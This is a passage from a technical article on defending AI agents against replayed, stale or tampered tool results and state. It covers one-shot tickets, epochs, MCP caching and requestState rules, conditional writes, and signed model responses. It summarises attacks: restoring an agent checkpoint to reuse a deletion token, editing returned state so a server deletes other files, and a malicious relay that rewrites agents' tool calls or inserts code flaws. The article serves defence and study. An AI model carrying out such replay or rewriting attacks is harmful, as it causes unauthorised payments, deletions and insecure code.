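A one-shot ticket authorizes a single action. The gateway stores each ticket, the session it belongs to and whether it has been used. When the agent proposes a change, such as a payment, the gateway checks that the ticket belongs to the current session and is unused, then marks it as used. A replayed result can still lead the agent to propose the wrong action, but the gateway refuses it because the old ticket belongs to another session or has already been used.

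The record of use has to be kept somewhere the agent can't reset. *ACRFence* (Zheng, Yang and colleagues, 2026) studies software that returns an agent to a saved earlier state, called a checkpoint, after an error or at a user's request. In one attack from the paper, a manager approves the deletion of one customer's data, and the agent receives a single-use token and deletes the data. A malicious employee then returns the agent to the moment just after the approval. The agent has the token again and no memory of having used it, and the employee tells it to delete another customer's data.

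In the simulation, a server that checked only the token's signature accepted both attempts to reuse a token. A server that kept a list of used tokens rejected every attempt. Two attempts is a very small sample, but the outcome follows from the design, because a signature remains valid after the first use.

The list must also remain intact after a restore. Zheng and colleagues cite a bug report about HashiCorp Vault, a program that stores secrets, in which a single-use token reappeared after someone restored the database from a snapshot.

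The model also should not generate the value that marks an action as a repeat. In another test by Zheng and colleagues, the agent generated the reference number that a simulated bank used to recognise repeated payments. After each of ten restores, the agent paid again with a new number, and the bank accepted the payment as new. The agent made no duplicate payments in ten runs without a restore.

A ticket still doesn't show whether the world has changed since it was issued. If the agent receives a ticket for INV-1042 on Monday and a colleague pays the invoice on Tuesday, the agent's ticket is still unused on Wednesday and would pass within the same session. The tickets stopped stale-context replay in the experiment because an earlier action had already used the replayed ticket. The experiment therefore did not test an unused ticket whose authorization had lapsed.

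#### A counter for the state of the world

The epoch defence closes that gap if the gateway detects the change. For each object, the gateway stores a counter called the world-state epoch and raises it whenever someone revokes an approval, completes an action or cancels one. Each result carries the counter's value from when the tool produced it. Before carrying out an action, the gateway compares that value with the current one.

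Suppose the counter for INV-1042 is at 7 on Monday. The colleague's payment on Tuesday raises it to 8. On Wednesday the agent proposes a payment based on Monday's result, and the gateway refuses it because the result's counter value, 7, doesn't match the current 8. The same comparison stops a duplicate payment, because the agent's own first payment also raises the counter.

It is less clear why the epoch stopped cross-task replay. If nobody has changed attachment A since task A, its counter is still current, so the rule should let the agent send the attachment. Zhi and colleagues' example result contains the value `epoch-F01-01-A`, which appears to include a letter for the attachment, so their gateway may have compared objects as well as states. A developer who stores a plain number for each object may not get the same protection.

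The counter can also be wrong when the gateway's information is incomplete. If the colleague pays through the bank's website and no program reports the payment to the gateway, the counter stays at 7 and Monday's result passes.

### Why matching the object is not enough

Zhi and colleagues tested a simpler check as a baseline. The gateway stores the identifier of the current task's object and compares it with the `object_id` in the result, once before the model reads the result and again when the agent proposes an action.

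This worked against cross-task replay in the file-sharing scenario. Task A had produced an approval for `report-north`, while task B concerned `report-south`, so the gateway withheld the approval. It failed against duplicate-effect replay, where the error rate was 100%. The agent had already shared `report-north`, and the replayed approval also concerned `report-north`, so both comparisons succeeded and the gateway allowed the agent to share the file again. Because the identifier is the same before and after the first share, the gateway would need a record of that share to tell the two situations apart.

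The baseline's recorded final-state error rate is zero for both stale-context and out-of-order replay, even though, according to Zhi and colleagues, the gateway accepted the forbidden action in all ten trials. They explain that the rate was zero only because the second phase reset the simulated system before the final measurement.

### The invoice under four checks

Suppose the agent retrieved invoices in one session on Monday and has to pay INV-1042 in a new session on Wednesday. The table shows how the checks apply as the paper describes them, assuming the epoch is a plain number and the gateway learns of every payment.

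| What the agent receives on Wednesday | Call id | One-shot ticket | Epoch | Object identifier |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Monday's reply about INV-1043 | Blocks the reply | Blocks the payment | Blocks the payment only if INV-1043 has changed | Blocks the reply |
| Monday's reply about INV-1042, which the agent or a colleague has since paid | Blocks the reply | Blocks the payment | Blocks the payment | Passes |
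| A reply to a new request for INV-1042, with Monday's data from a cache, after a colleague has paid | Passes | Passes | Blocks the payment only if the cache kept Monday's counter value | Passes |
| A reply to a new request for INV-1042, with the data of INV-1043 | Passes | Passes | Blocks the payment only if the data is out of date | Blocks the reply |

The last two rows are outside the four templates, which always replay an old result with its old identifiers. With an ordinary cache, the agent makes a new call, and the application often attaches the new call id to old data from the cache. Call-id matching then passes because the reply does answer the new call. If the gateway also issues a new ticket and adds the current counter value on delivery, those checks pass too. For the counter check to catch old data, the counter value must come from the stored record, like the time of measurement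 in the weather example.

The object check is still useful alongside the others. In the fourth row, a faulty lookup returned INV-1043 under the right call id. The object check catches this error, which call ids and tickets miss, as long as the tool copies the invoice number from the record it found and not from the request.

The templates also leave out forged and altered results. An attacker could change only `bank_account` in the current reply to the agent's own request. The call id would still match, the ticket would be unused, the counter would be current and the invoice number would be right, so all four checks would allow the payment to the attacker.

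## Cache lifetimes, clocks and changed facts

A world-state epoch does not account for changes that nobody reports to the gateway. The application can reduce the risk of acting on outdated data by setting a maximum age, but an ordinary MCP tool result has no standard field for the data's age.

### What MCP's caching fields cover

The July 2026 specification has two fields about reusing old data, `ttlMs` and `cacheScope`, which McCaffrey (2026) proposed in *TTL for List Results* (SEP-2549). Before these fields existed, servers notified clients of changes to their tool lists over a long-lived connection, which many clients and servers have trouble supporting. Without those notices, a client had no indication of how often to request the list again.

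`ttlMs` gives a lifetime ("time to live") in milliseconds. According to Model Context Protocol's *Caching* (2026), the client notes the time on its own clock when a response arrives and should treat the response as fresh while

now < t_received + ttlMs

In the specification's example, a list of tools has a `ttlMs` of 300,000, or five minutes. For those five minutes, the client may use its stored copy without asking the server. After that, it should fetch the list again when it next needs it, but it may use the expired copy if the fetch fails. A change notice ends the lifetime early. Under the specification, `ttlMs` is a hint, not a guarantee, because the server may change the data at any time.

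`cacheScope` limits who may receive the stored copy. A shared gateway may give a "public" response to any user, but it may reuse a "private" one only for the same authorization context, so a different access token needs a different cache. Model Context Protocol's *Caching hints*, a documentation page for the official Python library, describes the field as "a label, not a lock". If a server marks one customer's data as public by mistake, a gateway could give it to another customer. By default, the Python library sends a lifetime of 0 and the scope "private".

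Servers must include both fields in the completed results of six operations: `server/discover`, `tools/list`, `prompts/list`, `resources/list`, `resources/templates/list` and `resources/read`. McCaffrey's proposal and Model Context Protocol's *Key Changes* omit `server/discover`, but the official Python and C# libraries match the list of six.

Neither list includes `tools/call`, the operation that returns ordinary tool results. GenMCP, a library whose data types come from the official schema, gives a tool-call result the fields `_meta`, `content`, `isError`, `resultType` and `structuredContent`. A server could put a time in `_meta` or in the structured data, but the client would have to know where to find it and what it meant.

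A five-minute lifetime on the list of tools therefore suggests that `get_invoice` will still exist in five minutes, but gives no information about whether INV-1042 is still open. If the server also publishes the invoice as a resource, the response to a client's `resources/read` request includes a `ttlMs`, but the result of fetching the same invoice through a tool does not.

The Model Context Protocol also lets a tool result contain an embedded resource with an optional `lastModified` time. This time can't replace an age, because an invoice last modified in March may still be current in October, and the `lastModified` value in a copy cached on Monday can't reflect a payment made on Tuesday.

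Developers cache tool results anyway. FastMCP, a third-party Rust library that predates the July specification, has a caching component that keeps tool-call results for an hour by default. An agent that calls `get_invoice` through it could receive an hour-old status.

Even when a response has a `ttlMs`, the client counts from receipt and ignores any age the data already had. Suppose a gateway stores a public response with a lifetime of five minutes and passes it on after four, with the `ttlMs` unchanged. The client then counts another five minutes, so it may use data that is nine minutes old. HTTP caches handle this with an `Age` header, which gives the age of a stored response. The *Caching* page describes no equivalent and does not require the gateway to subtract the four minutes.

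The Python library is stricter than the specification because it limits every lifetime to 24 hours and reports an error when a fetch fails instead of using an expired copy. However, a request made just as a change notice arrives may receive the old copy once more.

### Observed, signed, used

Three times matter for a fact in a tool result. The observation time is when the source read the fact. The signing time is when a program made the message that reports it, and the time of use is when the agent acts on it. In the following example, the accounts system signs its replies but takes the status of an invoice from a cache:

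| Time | Event |
|---|---|
| 0 s | The accounts system reads INV-1042 from its database and caches the status "open" |
| 200 s | A colleague pays the invoice |
| 290 s | The accounts system answers the agent's request with the cached status and signs the reply |
| 310 s | The agent is about to pay |

Suppose the application has a freshness window of 300 seconds. If it counts from the signing time, the status is 20 seconds old, the check passes and the company pays twice. If it counts from the observation time, the status is 310 seconds old and the check fails. The application then has to get a new reading from the database, which would show the payment.

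The signature is valid in both cases. To make the second check possible, the accounts system must include the observation time in the data it signs. Even then, the recorded time can be too recent, because large systems often read from a copy of the database that lags behind the original. If the copy is 40 seconds behind, the result shows the original as it was 40 seconds before the recorded time.

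Checking the signing time is still useful because it limits how long someone can replay an intercepted message. An expiry time, like the one in MCP's `requestState`, also limits how long a message can be used, but it doesn't show how old the facts in the message are.

Checking the observation time wouldn't have helped if the agent had acted a little earlier. At 295 seconds, the status would have passed that check even though the colleague had paid 95 seconds before.

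### Clock error and dates in the future

The source and the application usually read different clocks, so the acceptance rule needs some tolerance:

−ε ≤ now − t ≤ Δ

Here *t* is the time in the message, Δ is the window and ε is the largest clock error the application tolerates. If the accounts system's clock is three seconds fast, a reading that arrives immediately has an age of about −3 seconds. The Python function for weather readings, which doesn't allow negative ages, would reject it. With ε set to five seconds, the reading passes.

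Clock error also affects the upper limit. If the source's clock is five seconds fast, a reading that is 305 seconds old appears to be 300 seconds old and passes. If an application must never use data older than 300 seconds and its clocks can differ by up to five seconds, it should set Δ to 295.

The lower limit on a record's age is easy to forget because people usually think of stale data as old. In *Instruction Self-Arbitration Is Not a Trust Boundary*, Leong (2026) describes a checker that examines an agent's stored records before the model reads them. The checker verifies a MAC that covers the record and its timestamp, and it rejects records more than 300 seconds old. In 150 trials, it rejected every record 400 seconds old. But in a separate set of tests, it accepted a record dated 600 seconds in the future, because the record's age came out as −600, which is less than 300.

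Such a record would have stayed acceptable for 900 seconds, three times the intended window, and a record dated a year ahead would have lasted more than a year. Leong fixed the flaw by rejecting any age below −5 seconds, which gives the rule above with ε = 5 and Δ = 300.

The test record had a valid MAC made with the system's own key, so an attacker would have needed that key or the help of an authorized program to use this flaw. An authorized program with a badly wrong clock could also produce such a record by accident.

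Within the window, the rule accepts the same message every time it arrives, so Leong's system also keeps a list of used records and makes each permission token valid for only one use. To test the tokens, Leong's program presented each one to its issuer again immediately after the model had used it, and the issuer rejected all 452.

The test shows that the list works while a single process keeps running. It doesn't cover a second session or a restart that erases the list. Outsiders can't repeat the test yet because Leong released no code or data with the revised paper. In that revision, Leong also withdrew several claims from the first version.

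### How long the window should be

A window of 300 seconds is a guess until someone compares it with how often the fact changes. Suppose the fact changes at random at an average rate λ. Divide its age *a* into *n* short intervals. The chance of no change in any one interval is about 1 − λa/n, so the chance of no change in all of them is about (1 − λa/n)ⁿ. As the intervals get shorter, this approaches exp(−λa). The chance that the fact has changed at least once is therefore

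1 − exp(−λa)

For a fact that changes once an hour on average and is five minutes old, λa is 1/12 and the chance that it has changed is about 8%. A developer can also choose an acceptable chance *p* and solve for the window, Δ = −ln(1 − p)/λ.

| Average rate of change | Chance of a change within 5 minutes | Window for a 1% chance |
|---|---|---|
| Once an hour | 8.0% | 36 seconds |
| Once a day | 0.35% | 14 minutes |
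| Once a week | 0.05% | 1 hour 41 minutes |

If a fact changes once an hour on average, a result cached for a full hour has a 63% chance of being out of date. The chance is lower for results used sooner. If the agent uses results of every age up to five minutes equally often, the average chance is about 4%.

The rate of change used must be that of the specific fact the agent relies on. Suppose a company has 200 open invoices at any time and pays 40 a week. A payment changes the list of open invoices about every four hours, but a particular invoice is paid at a rate of only once in 35 days. By that estimate, a five-minute-old status for one invoice would be wrong about once in 10,000 uses.

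That is probably too optimistic, because the agent doesn't pick invoices at random. It is told to pay INV-1042 when the invoice is due, which is also when a colleague is most likely to pay it. If the company makes most of its payments on Tuesday morning, a status read just before then carries much more risk than the weekly average. A better estimate would use the rate for due invoices at the busiest time of the week.

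The formula also assumes that the time of use does not depend on the change. An employee who knows that a manager has just revoked an approval can hurry to use it before the window closes. A short window leaves less time for this, but the application should look up an approval's current state when it acts.

The acceptable chance of using an outdated result depends on how much harm it could do. An hour-old temperature may be good enough for a conversation about the weather, but an 8% chance of paying 4,180 euros twice means an average loss of about 334 euros per payment if nobody recovers the money. A very short window can also block legitimate actions. In a rerun of Leong's experiments, a few model calls stalled for about ten minutes while the permission tokens lasted only 300 seconds, so a few tokens expired before the agent could make a legitimate deletion. A person approving a payment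 may also take that long. The application should fetch the invoice again after the approval, and ask for approval again if anything relevant has changed.

### When the fact changes just before the action

A shorter window can't eliminate the risk, because some time always passes between reading a fact and acting on it. The agent might read at noon that INV-1042 is open, the colleague might pay it half a second later, and the agent's own payment might arrive half a second after that. Programmers call this a time-of-check to time-of-use problem. Leong lists it among the things the checker's tests did not cover.

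A conditional write closes the gap by moving the comparison into the system that stores the record. HTTP supports this with the `If-Match` header, defined in the standard RFC 9110. For the invoice it works like this:

1. The application reads INV-1042. The accounts system returns the invoice with a version tag, `"7"`, in a header named `ETag`.
2. The colleague pays, and the accounts system changes the tag to `"8"`.
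3. The application asks the accounts system to mark the invoice as being paid, on condition that the tag is still `"7"`.
4. The accounts system finds `"8"`, changes nothing and answers with the code 412, "Precondition Failed".

The request in step 3 could look like this:

```http
PATCH /invoices/INV-1042 HTTP/1.1
Host: accounts.example
If-Match: "7"
Content-Type: application/merge-patch+json

{ "status": "paying" }
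```

The application then reads the invoice again and finds that it is paid. The check needs no clock or estimate of λ, but the accounts system must compare the tag and write the new status as one indivisible step in its database. Otherwise the colleague's payment could still be recorded between the comparison and the write.

The tag should change with every modification, even if the status later returns to its old value. If the colleague pays and then cancels the payment, the status goes from "open" to "paid" and back to "open". Comparing the statuses would show no difference, but the tag would have changed twice. Before anyone pays again, the manager may need to know why the colleague cancelled.

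`If-Match` applies to the record at the address in the request. If the application created a payment at `/payments`, the server would check the tag against that address, not against the invoice. Some servers ignore the header, so a developer should send a request with an outdated tag and confirm that it fails. A server can refuse writes that omit the header by returning HTTP status code 428, "Precondition Required".

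In an MCP application, the tool that changes the invoice would need a version argument, which its server could pass on as `If-Match`. The application's code should fill in this argument from the invoice the agent read. If the model instead supplied the latest version number, fetched just before the write, the write would succeed even though the payment decision was based on the old invoice.

The bank transfer happens in another system, which has no record of version 7. The example therefore changes the status to "paying", a new value that the invoice schema would have to allow, before ordering the transfer. Anyone else who tries to pay through the accounts system will find the invoice already marked as "paying", but a colleague who goes directly to the bank's website can still pay it a second time. If the agent crashes between the two steps, the invoice remains marked as "paying" with no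 transfer, so the company needs a way to find and settle such cases.

A conditional write also protects only the record whose version it compares. If the company keeps bank details in a separate supplier record, someone can change the account number while INV-1042 remains at version 7. To catch that change, the accounts system would have to check the supplier record's version in the same database transaction.

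## Returned state in MCP, tied to a user, a request and an expiry time

A conditional write works because the accounts system stores the current version of each record. Under the July 2026 specification, an MCP server can pause a job to get an answer from the user, storing nothing while it waits. It sends its working data to the client, which returns it with the answer. The client could change that data, so the specification sets much stricter rules for it than for an ordinary tool result.

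### How a tool asks a question

Before July, a server that needed an answer from the user kept the original call open and sent its question over the same connection. This was awkward for large services, which run many copies of a server behind a load balancer, a program that distributes requests among them. *SEP-2322* (Roth and McCaffrey, 2026) explains that the user's answer could reach copy B while copy A was waiting for it. To prevent this, the copies had to share a database, or the load balancer had to keep sending each client to the same copy. Either requirement is a burden for a simple tool. In the release announcement (Model Context Protocol, 2026), a Supabase manager says that this problem made it hard for the company's server to ask users for confirmation, and that the server can now do so, for example before a query that would delete data.

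The new mechanism is called a multi round-trip request. Model Context Protocol's *Multi Round-Trip Requests* describes these steps:

1. The client calls a tool.
2. The server ends the call with a result of type `input_required`. The result can contain questions, in `inputRequests`, and a string named `requestState`, which holds whatever the server needs to continue.
3. The client gets the answers, usually from the user.
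4. The client repeats the original call and adds the answers, in `inputResponses`, and the unchanged `requestState`.
5. Any copy of the server can read the state and finish the job.

The repeated call MUST have a new call id, so the id cannot link it to the first call. If the server has stored nothing, only the returned state links the two calls.

### Why the server can't trust its own data

In its post on the release candidate, Model Context Protocol (2026) illustrates the mechanism with a server that asks "Delete 3 files?" and sends this state:

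```text
eyJzdGVwIjoxLCJmaWxlcyI6WyJhIiwiYiIsImMiXX0=
```

This is plain base64, a way of writing data in ordinary characters that anyone can reverse. It decodes to:

```json
{"step":1,"files":["a","b","c"]}
```

Changing the `M` near the end of the string to a `Q` changes the file to be deleted from `c` to `d`. The user would agree to delete `c`, and a server that trusted the state would delete `d`.

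*Designing requestState for Multi Round-Trip Requests* (Körbächer, 2026) describes a worse change to a similar state. The client sets the step to 2 and replaces the list with `/etc/passwd`, a system file. The server resumes after its check of the answer and deletes a file that it never asked about.

Clients MUST return the state unchanged, but the server cannot verify that a client has done so. A dishonest user can write a client, and an attacker can take over an honest user's client. The server therefore MUST treat the state as attacker-controlled input, even though it created the original.

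Checking the user's permissions again before deleting each file would stop a user from deleting other people's files, but it would not stop a compromised client from deleting a file that its user is allowed to delete but wants to keep.

### What the specification requires

The rules for servers differ in strength:

| Protection | Strength |
|---|---|
| Treat returned state as attacker-controlled | MUST |
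| Protect its integrity and reject state that fails the check | MUST, if the state influences authorization, access to resources or business logic |
| Include the authenticated principal and reject state from anyone else | SHOULD |
| Include a short expiry time and reject late state | SHOULD |
| Identify the original request, for example by the method name and a digest of the important parameters, and reject state that arrives with another request | SHOULD |
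| Enforce single use on the server | MUST, if the server may accept the state only once |

For integrity, the specification suggests a MAC or authenticated encryption. Either would detect the change to the file list, but only encryption hides the file names from the client. Körbächer recommends encryption for sensitive state because clients may copy it into logs or conversation records.

In SEP-2322, Roth and McCaffrey only recommended encryption where tampering was a concern, but they required servers to bind any user-specific data to the user. The final specification requires integrity protection for any state that matters and only recommends binding to a user. Relaxing the binding requirement is strange, because a message authentication code (MAC) alone doesn't prevent one user from presenting another user's state.

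A server may omit integrity protection only when tampering can cause nothing worse than a failed request. Few useful states meet this condition, but a long random reference does if it points to a record that the server has stored with the user and the original request. If someone alters the reference, the server finds either no record or one for another user or request, and refuses the call. The file list needs integrity protection because altering it can make the server delete the wrong file.

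### A protected version of the file deletion

The release-candidate post shows only the server's reply. Suppose Alice's agent called `delete_files` with the folder `reports` and a minimum age of 90 days, and the server found files `a`, `b` and `c`. The list of files belongs in the state because the arguments don't contain it. If the server searched again after Alice's answer, it might find and delete a fourth file that she hadn't agreed to delete.

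The following functions protect the state with a MAC:

```python
def tag(body):
    return hmac.new(KEY, body.encode(), hashlib.sha256).hexdigest()

def digest(request):
    p = request["params"]
    parts = [request["method"], p["name"], p["arguments"]]
    text = json.dumps(parts, sort_keys=True)
    return hashlib.sha256(text.encode()).hexdigest()

def seal(state, user, request, now):
    claims = {"state": state, "user": user,
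              "expires": now + 600, "request": digest(request)}
    data = json.dumps(claims).encode()
    body = base64.urlsafe_b64encode(data).decode()
    return body + "." + tag(body)

def unseal(token, user, request, now):
    body, _, received = token.partition(".")
    if not hmac.compare_digest(received, tag(body)):
        raise ValueError("altered or forged")
    claims = json.loads(base64.urlsafe_b64decode(body))
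    if claims["user"] != user:
        raise ValueError("belongs to another user")
    if now >= claims["expires"]:
        raise ValueError("expired")
    if claims["request"] != digest(request):
        raise ValueError("belongs to another request")
    return claims["state"]
```

The server calls `seal` before it sends the question and `unseal` when the state comes back. `KEY` is a secret that all copies of the server share and no client has. `user` must come from the access token that the server has verified for the current call, not from an argument the client can fill in. `digest` leaves out the call id and the answers because these differ between the first call and the second.

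`unseal` checks the MAC before it reads anything else. Körbächer notes that this order matters because some programming languages can store program objects as data, and loading a forged object can run an attacker's code.

Suppose the server asks its question at 12:00. The functions then give these results:

- **Altered file list:** the client changes `c` to `d`. The MAC no longer matches, and the client can't compute a new one without the key.
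- **Another user:** Bob copies Alice's state from a shared log and sends it with his own access token. The MAC is valid, but the state names Alice, so the server rejects it.
- **Late return:** Alice answers at 12:11. The state expired at 12:10, so the server has to search the folder and ask again.
- **Another request:** the client sends the state with the folder `contracts`. The digests differ, and the server rejects it.
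- **Second use:** Alice agrees at 12:01, and the server deletes the files. At 12:05 a colleague saves a new file named `a` in the same folder. At 12:06 the client sends the same state and answer again, and the server deletes the new file.

A valid state shows that the server asked the question, but it doesn't prove that Alice answered it. The client writes `inputResponses`, so a compromised client can report that she agreed without showing her anything. Even with an honest client, the server has to check what the answer is as well as whether it fits the schema. Körbächer's version of the example requires a true-or-false field named `confirmed`, so a refusal, sent as `false`, also passes validation.

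### Why the second use passes

`unseal` takes four inputs: the state, the user, the request and the time. At 12:06 the first three are the same as at 12:01 and the time is still within the limit, so no check on these inputs could reliably distinguish a second use from a slow first one. The specification warns that its recommended fields don't guarantee single use.

As with the one-shot tickets described earlier, the server has to record which states have been used. It can add a random identifier to the protected state and, before deleting any files, insert that identifier into a database table that rejects duplicates. All copies of the server must use the same table. The server can remove an identifier once its state has expired, which keeps the table small.

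A draft MCP extension for file uploads uses the same method. In a post from November, Model Context Protocol (2026) describes servers that run jobs that must not run twice, such as deleting files. Before starting such a job, the server marks the state as used in a record that all copies of the server share. If it crashes after marking the state but before deleting the files, the files remain and the user has to confirm again. Marking the state afterwards would be worse, because a second call could arrive during the deletion.

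This brings back some of the shared storage that multi round-trip requests were designed to avoid. Körbächer proposes keeping such a record only for operations that need it, such as deletions, since reading the same file twice usually does no harm.

Accepting the state only once also doesn't protect a file that changes between the question and the answer. Protecting it requires a conditional write, which checks the version tag stored in the state for each file.

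### What the official libraries check

By default, the official Python library encrypts returned state with AES-256-GCM, a form of authenticated encryption, and checks the user, the expiry time, the method, the tool and a digest of the arguments, according to Model Context Protocol's *request_state*. The library also rejects state with an issue time too far in the future, the case that Leong's checker initially missed. The key exists only in one running process by default, so a developer who runs several copies of a server has to supply a shared key.

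The TypeScript library leaves it to the developer to protect the returned state. Model Context Protocol's *server/requestStateCodec*, which documents the beta of the library's second version, describes a helper that adds a message authentication code and an expiry time to the state. The helper can also bind the state to other information, but this is optional. The documentation's example binds it to the method and the client ID, which identifies the application but not necessarily the person using it. The method is `tools/call` for every tool, so this binding doesn't distinguish `delete_files` from any other tool.

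Applying the documented checks to the five tests gives:

| Test | Plain base64 | Python library | TypeScript helper with the example binding |
|---|---|---|---|
| Altered file list | Passes | Rejected | Rejected |
| Another user | Passes | Rejected if the server's token check identifies the user | Passes if both users' tokens have the same client id |
| Late return | Passes | Rejected after 10 minutes | Rejected after 10 minutes |
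| Another request | Passes | Rejected | Passes if it is also a tool call |
| Second use | Passes | Passes | Passes |

A developer can fix the two weak entries in the last column by including the user, the tool and the arguments in the binding. Neither library records which states a server has already accepted, so the developer has to add that record in both.

The Python library's ten-minute limit also applies to each question separately. If a tool asks three questions in a row, the library gives the state a new expiry time with each one, so a file list from the first call can be almost 30 minutes old when the tool acts. To limit the list's age, the server has to store the time of the original search in the state and check it before the tool acts.

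### Why MCP asks less of a tool result

An ordinary tool result travels in the other direction, from server to client, and MCP has far weaker rules for it. Under MCP, servers are to sanitise tool outputs, and clients SHOULD validate results before passing them to the model. MCP has no rule about a MAC, a principal, an expiry time or a digest of the request, and only the call id connects a result to its request.

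Part of this difference is justified. The server can check returned state because it wrote the original and holds the key. A client that asks for an invoice has no original to compare it with, and the accounts system is the authority on its own invoices. A MAC on the invoice would not correct a wrong amount. When the client connects directly, HTTPS already prevents outsiders from changing the reply. To check a signature, the client would also have to get the server's public key from a source it trusts, whereas the server can check its own state without sharing a key.

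This argument depends on the server owning the data and connecting directly to the client, but often neither is true. The July revision makes gateways easier to use by putting the method and tool name in HTTP headers, where a gateway can read them to route and authorize calls. If the HTTPS connection ends at the gateway, the gateway can change a result or deliver an old one, and the client's connection still looks secure. A cache can also return an old invoice. A weather or search tool has no authority over the readings or pages it passes on.

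A server that is the authority on an invoice can still send its reply to the wrong client. In the TypeScript vulnerability described earlier, an honest server could send client A's answer to client B because both had used the same call id. If the answer had included A's identity and a digest of A's request, B could have compared them with its own and rejected the answer.

The stricter rules would therefore add little when a client reads a company's own records over a direct connection. They would be worth adding when a result passes through a gateway or shared cache and leads to a payment, because changing the bank account in a result can do as much harm as changing a file name in returned state.

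## Signed responses and tool receipts

A gateway can also stand between an agent and its language model. Many developers send model requests through a relay, a service that forwards them to a provider such as Anthropic or OpenAI. They do this to lower costs, get around regional restrictions or reach several providers through one address. In *Rewriting the Response Path*, Luo, Zhang and colleagues (2026) studied what a dishonest relay can do to the model's answers and how a signature could prevent it.

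### A relay between the agent and its model

The relay reads the model name in each request, forwards the request to the right provider and passes the answer back, so it has every message in readable form. Suppose the model generates a tool call to pay 4,180 euros into Brandt Paper's account. A malicious relay could replace the account number with a thief's and leave the rest unchanged. The altered call still fits the schema, so the agent's software carries it out as if the model had written it. Training the model to refuse harmful requests doesn't help, because the change happens after the model has generated the call.

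Luo and colleagues looked at the 60 most-used applications on OpenRouter, a service that routes requests to many models. A custom address made sense for 25 of them, and 23 of those accept one or accept the user's own credentials. These 23 applications permit a relay, but the count does not show how many users have one. Luo and colleagues also cite an earlier measurement of 428 relays, in which 9 injected code into responses and 17 accessed credentials that its researchers had planted.

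On a relay that the researchers ran themselves, changing one field redirected the agent in 89.1% of tasks from the Agent Security Bench, averaged over five models. They also tested whether an altered program could pass its public tests and still contain a security flaw. In a collection of programming exercises, 99.7% of the altered solutions that passed had the flaw. For 60 repairs to Django, a web framework, the hidden security check failed in 69.0% of cases, and the public tests passed in 51.7%. Luo and colleagues describe the 69.0% as cases in which the public tests still passed, but at most 51.7% of cases could have had both outcomes.

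Filters that look for suspicious content caught few of the changes. The best one, which flags improbable text, detected 30% of the altered exercise solutions at a false-alarm rate of 5%. The thief's account number is hard for a filter to detect because it looks as ordinary as the supplier's.

### Why TLS does not settle the matter

HTTPS connections use TLS, a protocol that encrypts the data and lets the client verify, through a certificate, which server it has reached. With a relay, there are two such connections, one from the agent to the relay and one from the relay to the provider. TLS works properly on both, so no outsider can read or change the data on the way, and the agent can be confident that it has reached the relay.

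However, the relay decrypts the provider's answer and encrypts it again for the agent. The agent can't use TLS to check whether the relay changed the answer, because TLS authenticates the relay, not the origin of the data it passes on. The same is true of a tool result that passes through an MCP gateway.

The agent and the provider could encrypt the whole message so that only they could read it. But this would hide the model's name, which the relay needs to choose a provider.

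### What the provider signs

The scheme that Luo and colleagues propose, sign-c, leaves the routing information readable and signs the part that the agent will act on. It adds a gateway in front of the model and a small program called a shim beside the agent. The signature covers

b = (s, t, H(κ(q)), H(κ(c)))

Here *s* is the session, *t* the turn within it, *q* the request and *c* the tool calls in the answer. H computes a digest, and κ puts the data into a canonical form, which the next subsection explains. One exchange works like this:

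1. The shim signs the request and sends it through the relay.
2. The gateway checks the shim's signature and passes the request to the model.
3. The gateway computes *b* from the request it received and the tool calls the model wrote, and signs it.
4. The relay passes the answer and the signature to the shim.
5. The shim computes *b* again from the request it sent and the tool calls that arrived. If the signature doesn't fit, the shim discards the answer before the agent acts.

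If the relay changes the account number, the digest of the tool calls changes and the signature no longer matches. An old answer with a genuine signature also fails, because it was signed for a different session or turn.

#### Canonical forms

Honest relays often rewrite JSON without changing its meaning. These two lines contain the same data:

```json
{"invoice_number": "INV-1042", "amount": 4180.0}
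{"amount":4180,"invoice_number":"INV-1042"}
```

Their digests differ, so a signature over the exact characters of the first line would fail on the second. A canonical form is a fixed way of writing data that gives equal data the same characters. The JSON Canonicalization Scheme, a published standard, sorts the field names, removes the spaces and writes numbers in a standard format, so both lines become the second one.

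The function κ keeps the tool calls in order, each with its identifier, name and arguments, and the reason the model stopped. It omits the model's explanatory text, so a relay can reformat that text without breaking the signature, but it can also change what the text says. If the model warned that the bank account differs from last month's, a dishonest relay could delete the warning, and a manager who relied on the text might approve the payment.

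Tool results go the other way, inside the agent's next request to the model. Luo and colleagues describe κ only in terms of tool calls and the reason for stopping, so it is unclear whether a request's signature covers the tool results in it. An optional layer of authenticated encryption should protect the entire message body in both directions.

#### Missing signatures

A relay could remove the signature. The shim can treat a missing signature as an attack only if it already has the provider's public key and a record that this provider signs its answers. It can fetch both directly from the provider's domain, but on networks where all traffic goes through the relay, they have to come with the shim's installation package.

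The relay can still refuse to forward an answer, but the user will notice. The protection fails if the relay's operator also supplies the shim and no independent party has signed the package.

### Tests, costs and adoption

Luo and colleagues replayed 353 altered exercise solutions and 58 altered Django patches, and the shim rejected all of them. They also tested the defence on AgentDojo, a benchmark with simulated banking, office, messaging and travel tasks. With Claude Opus 4.6, the defence lowered the attack's success rate from 74.6% to zero. The agent completed 80.9% of its own tasks under attack with the defence, compared with 87.2% with no attack. Luo and colleagues give no reason for the difference.

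The shim rejected none of 694 honest AgentDojo responses. With a sample of that size, the true false-rejection rate could still be as high as about 0.4%. The larger uncertainty comes from relay changes that the test left out. It covered reordered fields and changed spacing, but not responses that a relay reassembles from streamed fragments or translates between providers' formats. A relay that serves several providers may need to do both.

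The signing, checking and encryption added a median of 2.97 milliseconds per call, or 0.0167% of the model's median response time of 17.8 seconds. For a model that answers in one second, the share would still be negligible, at about 0.3%.

Adoption is the harder part. The provider has to create a key pair, sign every response and publish its public key. The user has to install the shim, but the agent and the model's interface don't have to change. Luo and colleagues write that a single provider or user can adopt the scheme alone, but a user gains nothing until the provider signs. No provider took part in the experiment; the researchers ran the signing gateway themselves, along with new-api, a popular open-source relay program. They suggest that a provider could send the signature in an HTTP header, which clients without the shim would ignore.

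### Receipts made by the agent's own runtime

A signature from the provider shows which tool calls the model wrote, but not whether the model later reports the results correctly. Basu (2026), in *Tool Receipts, Not Zero-Knowledge Proofs*, addresses that problem with a system called NabaOS. Its runtime, the program that carries out the agent's tool calls, makes a receipt for each call and adds a message authentication code (MAC) made with a secret key. The model sees the tool's output and the receipt's identifier, but not the key. Another program then compares the model's statements with the receipts.

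| Field of the receipt | Content | Covered by the MAC |
|---|---|---|
| `id` | Identifier of the receipt | Yes |
| `tool_name` | Name of the tool | Yes |
| `input_hash` | Digest of the arguments in canonical form | Yes |
| `output_hash` | Digest of the raw output | Yes |
| `timestamp_ms` | Time of the call | Yes |
| `result_count` | Number of results | No |
| `facts` | Values taken from the output, such as a sender or a price | No |
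| `duration_ms` | Duration of the call | No |

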